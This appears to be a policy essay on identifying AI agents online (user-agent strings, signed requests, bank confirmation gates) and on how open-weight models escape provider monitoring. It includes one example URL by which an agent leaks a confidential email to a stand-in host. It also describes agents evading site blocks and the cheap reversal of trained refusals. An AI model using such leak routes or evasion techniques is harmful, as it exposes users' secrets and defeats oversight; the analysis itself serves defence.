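Rinehart describes a compromise proposed by Andrey Fradkin and Alex Imas, which would give users the right to deploy an agent that works through their own browser and login, acts only at their direction, identifies itself, and collects no more data than the transaction needs. Rinehart thinks such a mandate would be premature and would override private contracts. He also objects that shops never planned for customers that work faster than humans and can run in many copies at once. A cap on requests per account would answer much of that objection. Requiring agents to identify themselves is more difficult, and it was the central issue in the dispute over Comet.

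### Telling an agent from a person

The simplest way to recognise an agent is by its user-agent string, a line of text every browser sends to name the program making the request. Modern Retail's *The Amazon Effect* (2025) reports that Amazon added rules against two OpenAI programs by name, including ChatGPT-User, which fetches pages when somebody asks ChatGPT a question. But a program can send any name. JD Supra's *Amazon Claims It’s a Victim of AI Lockpicking* reports Amazon's allegation that Comet identified itself as Google Chrome.

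A site can also look for indirect signs of an agent, such as how the pointer moves, how fast the visitor types and which network the request comes from. A site may be able to identify an agent that runs in a data centre by its network address. Comet is harder to spot because it runs on the customer's laptop and uses the customer's own connection and login. Stein expects agents to spread through online spaces designed for people, where sites can't easily tell them from human users.

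Amazon has had some success at blocking AI agents. It identified and blocked the assistant in Perplexity's Comet browser at first, and the two companies dispute whether Perplexity then knowingly changed the user-agent string to get back in. Amazon's employees spent many hours building tools to detect and block Comet. In September 2026 Amazon also blocked Muse, even though Amazon says Muse doesn't identify itself.

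These cases show that a very large company can recognise a particular popular agent if it makes the effort, but they don't show how many agents got through or how many human shoppers Amazon blocked by mistake. A small shop can't afford the same work, and a home-built agent has no known pattern to look for.

### Signing a request

Cryptography can prevent one agent from posing as another. An agent's operator creates two linked keys: a private key that makes signatures and a public key that can check them but can't make them. Suppose a company at the address agents.example runs a shopping agent:

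1. The company keeps the private key secret and publishes the public key on its website.
2. When the agent requests a page from a shop, the company's software signs a short statement that gives the company's address, the shop's address and the time:

```http
GET /basket HTTP/1.1
Host: shop.example
Signature-Agent: "https://agents.example"
Signature-Input: sig=("@authority" "signature-agent");
  created=1796428800;expires=1796428860;keyid="key-1"
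Signature: sig=:[the signature itself]:
```

3. The shop fetches the public key from agents.example and checks the signature. The check fails if somebody has changed the signed details or used a different private key.
4. The shop confirms that the signature names this shop and hasn't expired. Here it lasts sixty seconds, so a thief who copies it can't use it at another shop or on another day.
5. The shop now knows which company is responsible for the request, and it can refuse the agent, admit it or limit what it may do.

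The signature doesn't show which model the agent uses or whom it is acting for. Agent IDs, which Stein mentions as a proposed response to agents that resemble human users, could add this information. An ID might include the model, the customer, and a safety-test result signed by the tester, which a bank could check.

Signed requests identify only agents whose operators choose to sign. People's browsers don't normally sign their requests, so an unsigned request could come from a person or an agent. A shop that refused every unsigned request would lose its human customers. It could ask all visitors to prove they are human, but that would annoy them and reduce their privacy, and a person could pass the check and then hand the browser to an agent.

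Signing is also less secure when the agent runs on the user's machine. If the operator ships the private key inside the program, a skilled user can extract it and sign requests from a different agent. The operator can keep the key on its servers and sign each request there, but then it has to check that the request came from its program.

Whether operators sign will depend on how shops treat signed agents. Amazon could have used a string identifying Comet to block it, so Perplexity had good reason not to send one. If signed agents got a faster checkout and fewer interruptions, most commercial operators would probably sign. Identification therefore works better for enforcing conditions that an agent can meet, like Shopify's, than for enforcing a ban like eBay's. A law could force companies such as Meta to sign, but it would do little about agents that hobbyists run at home.

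### Gating the payment instead of the browser

A service can avoid having to identify agents by applying the same check to an action whoever performs it. For example, Stein suggests requiring human authentication for large transfers and steps such as legal registrations.

Suppose a homeowner asks a browser agent to pay a roofer's £4,800 bill. The bill arrived by email, and a fraudster has changed the account number on it.

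1. The agent opens the bank's website in the homeowner's browser, where the homeowner is already logged in. To the bank, this looks like a customer on their usual laptop.
2. The agent copies the account number from the bill, enters the amount and clicks "Pay".
3. The bank holds the payment, because its rules require confirmation for any payment above £500 and for the first payment to any new account.
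4. The bank sends a request to the homeowner's phone that shows the amount and the name on the receiving account. The agent controls the browser but not the phone, so it can't answer.
5. The homeowner sees a stranger's name and declines. Had the name been the roofer's, a fingerprint would have released the money.

This gate passes all three tests of enforceability, even though the bank never finds out that an agent was involved. The drawback is that people who make their own payments have to confirm them too.

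The threshold needs some care. Without the rule about new accounts, an agent could split the bill into ten payments of £480 and never trigger a confirmation. The bank could apply the limit to each day's total instead, but that would still let through:

£500 × 30 days = £15,000 a month

The rule about new accounts closes most of this gap, since a thief's account is new to the victim the first time.

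The agent also must not be able to control the phone. Stein lists remote control of mobile phones among the general-purpose tools behind the growth in action tools from registered companies. An agent controlling both the browser and the phone could approve its own payment if the bank required only a tap on the screen. A fingerprint or a code from a separate card reader is harder for software to supply.

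Finally, the homeowner has to read the message. People approve requests carelessly when an agent interrupts them fifty times in a session, but a bank that asks about one large payment a month has a better chance of getting their attention.

### Acts that nobody checks

Checking the act works only if some company controls it and can recognise it as important. Many harmful things an agent can do with a browser consist of steps that look trivial. For example, an agent that is logged in to its user's mailbox can read a confidential message and then open a web address that contains the text:

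```text
https://notes.example/save?text=Offer+to+buy+Harlow+Ltd+for+12m
```

The mail host sees its customer reading an email, and the website receives the secret in an ordinary page request, so neither has a reason to ask for a fingerprint. An employer could block unfamiliar websites, but a person using their own laptop usually has nobody to do that for them.

Other harm comes from volume. One fake product review does little damage, but 10,000 can ruin a small business, and an agent can spread them over many sites so that no site receives more than a few. Requiring a fingerprint for every review would prevent this but also stop most honest reviewers.

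Cryptocurrency payments are harder to gate than bank transfers. If the agent holds the secret key to a wallet, the network will accept any payment the agent signs, and there is no bank to delay it. The owner can keep the key on a separate device that requires a button press to sign, but the owner has to choose to do this.

Somebody also has to decide in advance which actions are consequential. Banks have had decades to learn which payments are suspicious, but few website operators have had to think about what an agent might do with a comment box or a search field.

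## Models that anyone can run

All of the model provider's controls, from trained refusals to closed accounts, depend on the model running on machines that the provider manages. When a developer publishes a model's weights, the numbers the model learned in training, anyone with enough hardware can run a copy, and the developer never sees what that copy does.

If the group that used Claude Code for espionage in 2025 had run an open-weight model on its own servers, its MCP servers would have worked just as well, because MCP doesn't depend on which model generates the requests. But no AI company would have received those requests, so none could have noticed the pattern or closed the group's accounts.

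Switching models can take a two-line change in the host application's settings:

```json
{
  "model": "name-of-an-open-weight-model",
  "model_address": "http://10.0.0.5:8000",
  "mcpServers": {
    "mail": { "command": "npx", "args": ["example-mail-server"] }
  }
}
```

The address here belongs to a machine on the user's own network. The entry for the mail server stays the same.

### What the developer can still withhold

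*How Far Behind the Frontier are Leading Open Weight Models on Cyber?* (UK AI Security Institute, July 2026) explains that a developer who releases a model's weights permanently loses the ability to monitor its use, control who has access or withdraw it. The model's trained refusals come with the weights, but users can often reverse them. A joint report by the House Homeland Security Committee and the House committee on the Chinese Communist Party (2026) says that reversing them in one recent Chinese model takes a few thousand dollars of computing. Only one person has to pay this, because others can then download the altered copy.

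Some users won't need an altered copy. CAISI, the US government's AI testing centre, found that the safeguards on GLM-5.2, a model from the Chinese company Zhipu, allow it to help develop cyberattacks.

The developer's last chance to withhold anything is before release. In October 2026 Moonshot, another Chinese company, said it had cut hacking data before releasing the weights of its strongest model, Kimi K3.1 Pro (Constantin, *Moonshot releases Kimi K3.1 Pro and says it cut its hacking skills*, 2026). The model evidently kept a lot of hacking skill, since AISI's *Kimi K3.1 Pro performs comparably to Claude Mythos 5* (2026) reports that it matched Anthropic's Mythos 5 at attacking three simulated networks. Hacking draws heavily on ordinary programming skill, which Moonshot had good reason to keep.

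### How far behind open models are

The provider's gate matters most for work that open models can't yet do. *How Far Behind Are Open-Weight Models?* (Raschka, 2026) measured the lag by finding when a publicly available closed model first reached an open model's score on a general index. On 3 December 2026, Kimi K3.1 Pro was 93 days behind, and Amazon's Ergo, released two days earlier, was 177 days behind.

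The lag grows between releases because an open model's score stays fixed as time passes. Kimi was only 64 days behind when Moonshot published its weights on 4 November.

Other estimates rely on different tests. *Open-weight models*, by the research group Epoch AI, collects the group's comparisons, which combine many benchmarks into one index. Mozilla's *The State of Open Source AI* (2026) uses data on the length of tasks an agent can complete, measured by how long a person would need. For hacking, AISI has its own tests, and Barry's *Open-weight models trail closed models in cyber capabilities by 6–7 months* describes an index that Epoch AI built.

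| Ability | Source | Date of estimate | Lag of the best open models |
|---|---|---|---|
| General | Raschka | December 2026 | 3 months |
| General | Epoch AI | May 2026 | 4 months |
| Length of agent tasks | Mozilla | September 2026 | 4.4 months |
| Hacking | AISI | July 2026 | 4 to 7 months |
| Hacking | Barry | October 2026 | 6 to 7 months |

AISI's December results suggest that the hacking gap has broadly held since July.

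A few months can make a considerable difference to how long an agent can work alone. Mozilla estimates that the length of task closed models can handle doubles every 5.5 months. A lag of 4.4 months therefore means that closed models can handle tasks about 1.7 times as long:

2^(4.4 ÷ 5.5) ≈ 1.74

Mozilla also finds that open models are doubling faster, every 3.9 months. If both trends continued, open models would catch up in about 11 months. That seems doubtful, since Epoch AI put the general lag at around three months in October 2025 and four months in May 2026.

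The lag also depends on whether developers can see the test. *How far behind are open models?*, an analysis of 17 benchmarks, puts the lag at four to six months on public tests but eight to ten on private ones. Amazon (2026) published scores for Ergo that show a similar pattern. The scores also cover Mistral Large 4, from the French company Mistral, and two closed models, OpenAI's GPT-5.5 from April 2026 and Anthropic's Claude Fable 5.2 from November.

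| Test | Ergo | Kimi K3.1 Pro | Mistral Large 4 | GPT-5.5 | Fable 5.2 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Public coding tasks (DeepSWE) | 74.2 | 77.9 | 59.1 | 69.2 | 75.2 |
| Public professional tasks (AutomationBench-AA) | 70.0 | 73.3 | 57.8 | 47.3 | 76.4 |
| Amazon's private software tasks | 65.4 | 58.6 | 39.4 | 55.3 | 78.7 |
| Amazon's private very long tasks | 20.5 | 13.1 | 7.5 | 7.3 | 72.6 |

The best open models score about as well as Fable 5.2 on the public tests. But Fable 5.2 scores more than three times as high as any of them on the very long tasks, which are closest to what an autonomy gate on running time would control. Amazon drew the private tasks from its own businesses, so Ergo's lead over Kimi on those tasks deserves some suspicion, but Amazon had little reason to make its own model look worse than Anthropic's.

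Even so, all three open models scored at least slightly higher than GPT-5.5 had on the very long tasks. Closed models improved so quickly during 2026 that a lag of several months meant a very large gap in scores.

### Businesses that have already switched

Most people who switch away from a provider that gates autonomy probably aren't doing so to escape the gate. The House Homeland Security Committee examined three American companies that use Chinese open-weight models: Airbnb, DoorDash and Anysphere, which makes the coding tool Cursor. It attributes the wider trend to low prices, near-frontier performance and the freedom to customise the models. Bot Mutiny's *Airbnb, DoorDash, Cursor Use Chinese AI, House Says* (2026) reports the committee's finding that one Airbnb assistant, built on Alibaba's Qwen models, handles roughly 80,000 exchanges a day with guests and hosts.

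The committee is mainly worried about dependence on China, but it also found that a company can download a model, adapt it, rename it and build it into a product without disclosing where it came from. This affects gates because it makes it even harder for a bank or a regulator to tell which model an agent runs on.

### The machines a leading model needs

Downloading a model is much easier than running it. Kimi K3.1 Pro has 2.8 trillion parameters, the individual numbers that make up its weights, according to 问舟 (2026), in *月之暗面 2.8 万亿参数 Kimi K3.1 Pro 开放权重，登顶 Agent Arena 开源模型榜*. At full precision each takes two bytes, and a compressed version uses half a byte:

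2.8 trillion × 2 bytes = 5.6 terabytes

2.8 trillion × 0.5 bytes = 1.4 terabytes

To run at a useful speed, the model has to fit in fast memory. A powerful consumer graphics card might have 32 gigabytes of it, so even the compressed version would need about 44 cards. Ergo is smaller, but its most compact form is 626 gigabytes, according to TrustList's *Ergo*, and would still fill 20 cards.

Hardware requirements keep the leading open models off nearly all home computers, though only for a while. Epoch AI found in August 2025 that models small enough to run on a consumer graphics card matched the performance of the best models within a year. A government or a well-funded criminal group can also buy or rent a server powerful enough to run the leading open models.

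### Hosts as gates

Many users pay a host for API access to an open model instead of running it themselves. The host runs the model on its own machines, as Amazon does with Ergo on its Bedrock service, and receives the same text that a closed model's provider would. It can run classifiers, check who its customers are and close accounts, so it can see the connection and refuse it.

However, a host's refusal has much less effect than a refusal by Anthropic, because the customer can get exactly the same open model from another host. Nobody else can supply Claude Mythos without Anthropic's agreement. If nine out of ten hosts refused an agent, its owner would spend an afternoon finding the tenth and perhaps pay a little more.

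Hosts also compete by promising not to inspect what their customers do. TrustList reports that Amazon offers Ergo with no data retention, so Amazon would probably miss the kind of campaign that Anthropic stores data for 30 days to detect.

A customer can avoid a host's checks altogether by renting a bare server and installing the model on it. The cloud company knows who is paying and how heavily the chips are used, but it doesn't normally read the conversations.

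A law could make hosts a stronger gate by requiring all of them to verify customers who run the most capable models. That would reach most careless users and many small criminals, who need somebody else's hardware, but not people who use hosts in countries without such a law or who own a server.

### What a lead of a few months is worth

People draw opposite conclusions from these facts. Some argue that a single capable model without a gate defeats every provider's gate, since anyone Anthropic refuses can use the open model instead. The open model only has to be good enough for the harm in question. CNAS (2026), an American security think tank, similarly argues that governments should judge Chinese AI by what it can do, "not just how far behind" it is.

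This reading assumes that open models are already capable enough to cause the harm in question. That is clearly true for some harms, such as invoice fraud. Any recent model can write a convincing fake invoice, so a provider that refuses to write one protects hardly anybody.

On the other reading, a gate on the strongest models gives defenders time to prepare. AISI describes the lag between closed and open models as time for defenders to use the best closed models before the same abilities become available without safeguards. Anthropic gave the same reason for Project Glasswing. This reasoning holds only if today's open models are not capable enough to cause the harm, and if defenders can finish preparing before open models are.

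How much the time is worth depends on how fast the defender can move. Suppose closed models gain a dangerous hacking skill in January and open models have it five months later. A software company that needs six weeks to repair its product is safe with time to spare. A hospital that replaces its computers every eight years will have replaced few of them:

5 months ÷ 96 months ≈ 5%

Some defenders are too slow to deliver a fix even after they have written it. In October 2026 Epoch AI reported that Zhipu's GLM-5.3 could turn security fixes for the Firefox browser into working attacks before the fixes reached users. Each attack cost roughly $1,000.

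The House Homeland Security Committee cites public reports that an attacker used an open-source hacking tool and a model from the Chinese company DeepSeek to break into several of South Korea's largest banks and other financial institutions within days. If the attacker ran the model privately, no provider could have interrupted the attack.

Open models can help defenders too. Hugging Face used GLM-5.2 to defend itself when OpenAI's agent broke in, according to The Next Web's *Open-weight AI caught the frontier on capability. On safety, it didn’t*. Hugging Face's chief executive, Clem Delangue, argues that a system that stops one attack can stop millions more. Papadatos, also quoted in the article, calls this overstated because a ransomware gang can change its methods in a week and a hospital can't.

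A permanent lead could help against hacking indefinitely, because defenders would always have better tools than most attackers. It's less useful against a harm that a stronger model can't repair, such as an engineered disease. The lead only delays that danger, unless people use the time to build a lasting defense, such as a stock of vaccines.

Governments can also accidentally shorten closed models' lead over open ones. The White House has a voluntary scheme for reviewing some closed models for hacking risk, but it reportedly doesn't cover open models. If reviews delayed only closed models, by two months, the lag between the public release of closed models and comparable open ones would shrink by up to two months, although defenders with early access would keep their advantage.

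Neither reading is much help in understanding accidents. An agent needs no special skill to delete the wrong folder, and a weaker model may well do it more often.

### What still binds an agent on an open model

Gates that don't depend on the model provider still work with open models. A bank checks the access token and asks for a fingerprint, whichever model chose the payment's recipient. The table covers an agent that runs on a private copy of an open model.

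| What the agent attempts | Who can still stop it | What the loss of the provider changes |
|---|---|---|
| Pay a new recipient from its user's bank account | The bank | Very little |
| Send a company's customer list outside | The employer | Very little, if the traffic passes through a gateway |
| Send fake invoices from newly opened accounts | Each mail host, and the victims' banks | Nobody sees the whole campaign being written |
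| Delete files on its owner's laptop | The owner | The model may no longer refuse |
| Break into a hospital | The hospital | Nobody can cut the agent off from its model |

Some evidence also disappears. When an agent pays a fake invoice emailed by a stranger, no provider can connect the email to the payment any more. Only the host application can, and it usually belongs to the agent's owner.

An employer that runs an open model for its staff is in a better position, because it takes over the provider's role. It receives every conversation and can add its own classifiers, limit how long agents run and withdraw the model from anyone who misuses it. No outside company can change the model or cut off access, which AISI considers a benefit of open weights. But the employer has to do the monitoring that Anthropic or OpenAI would otherwise do, and a firm that chose the model to save money may not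 want to pay for that.
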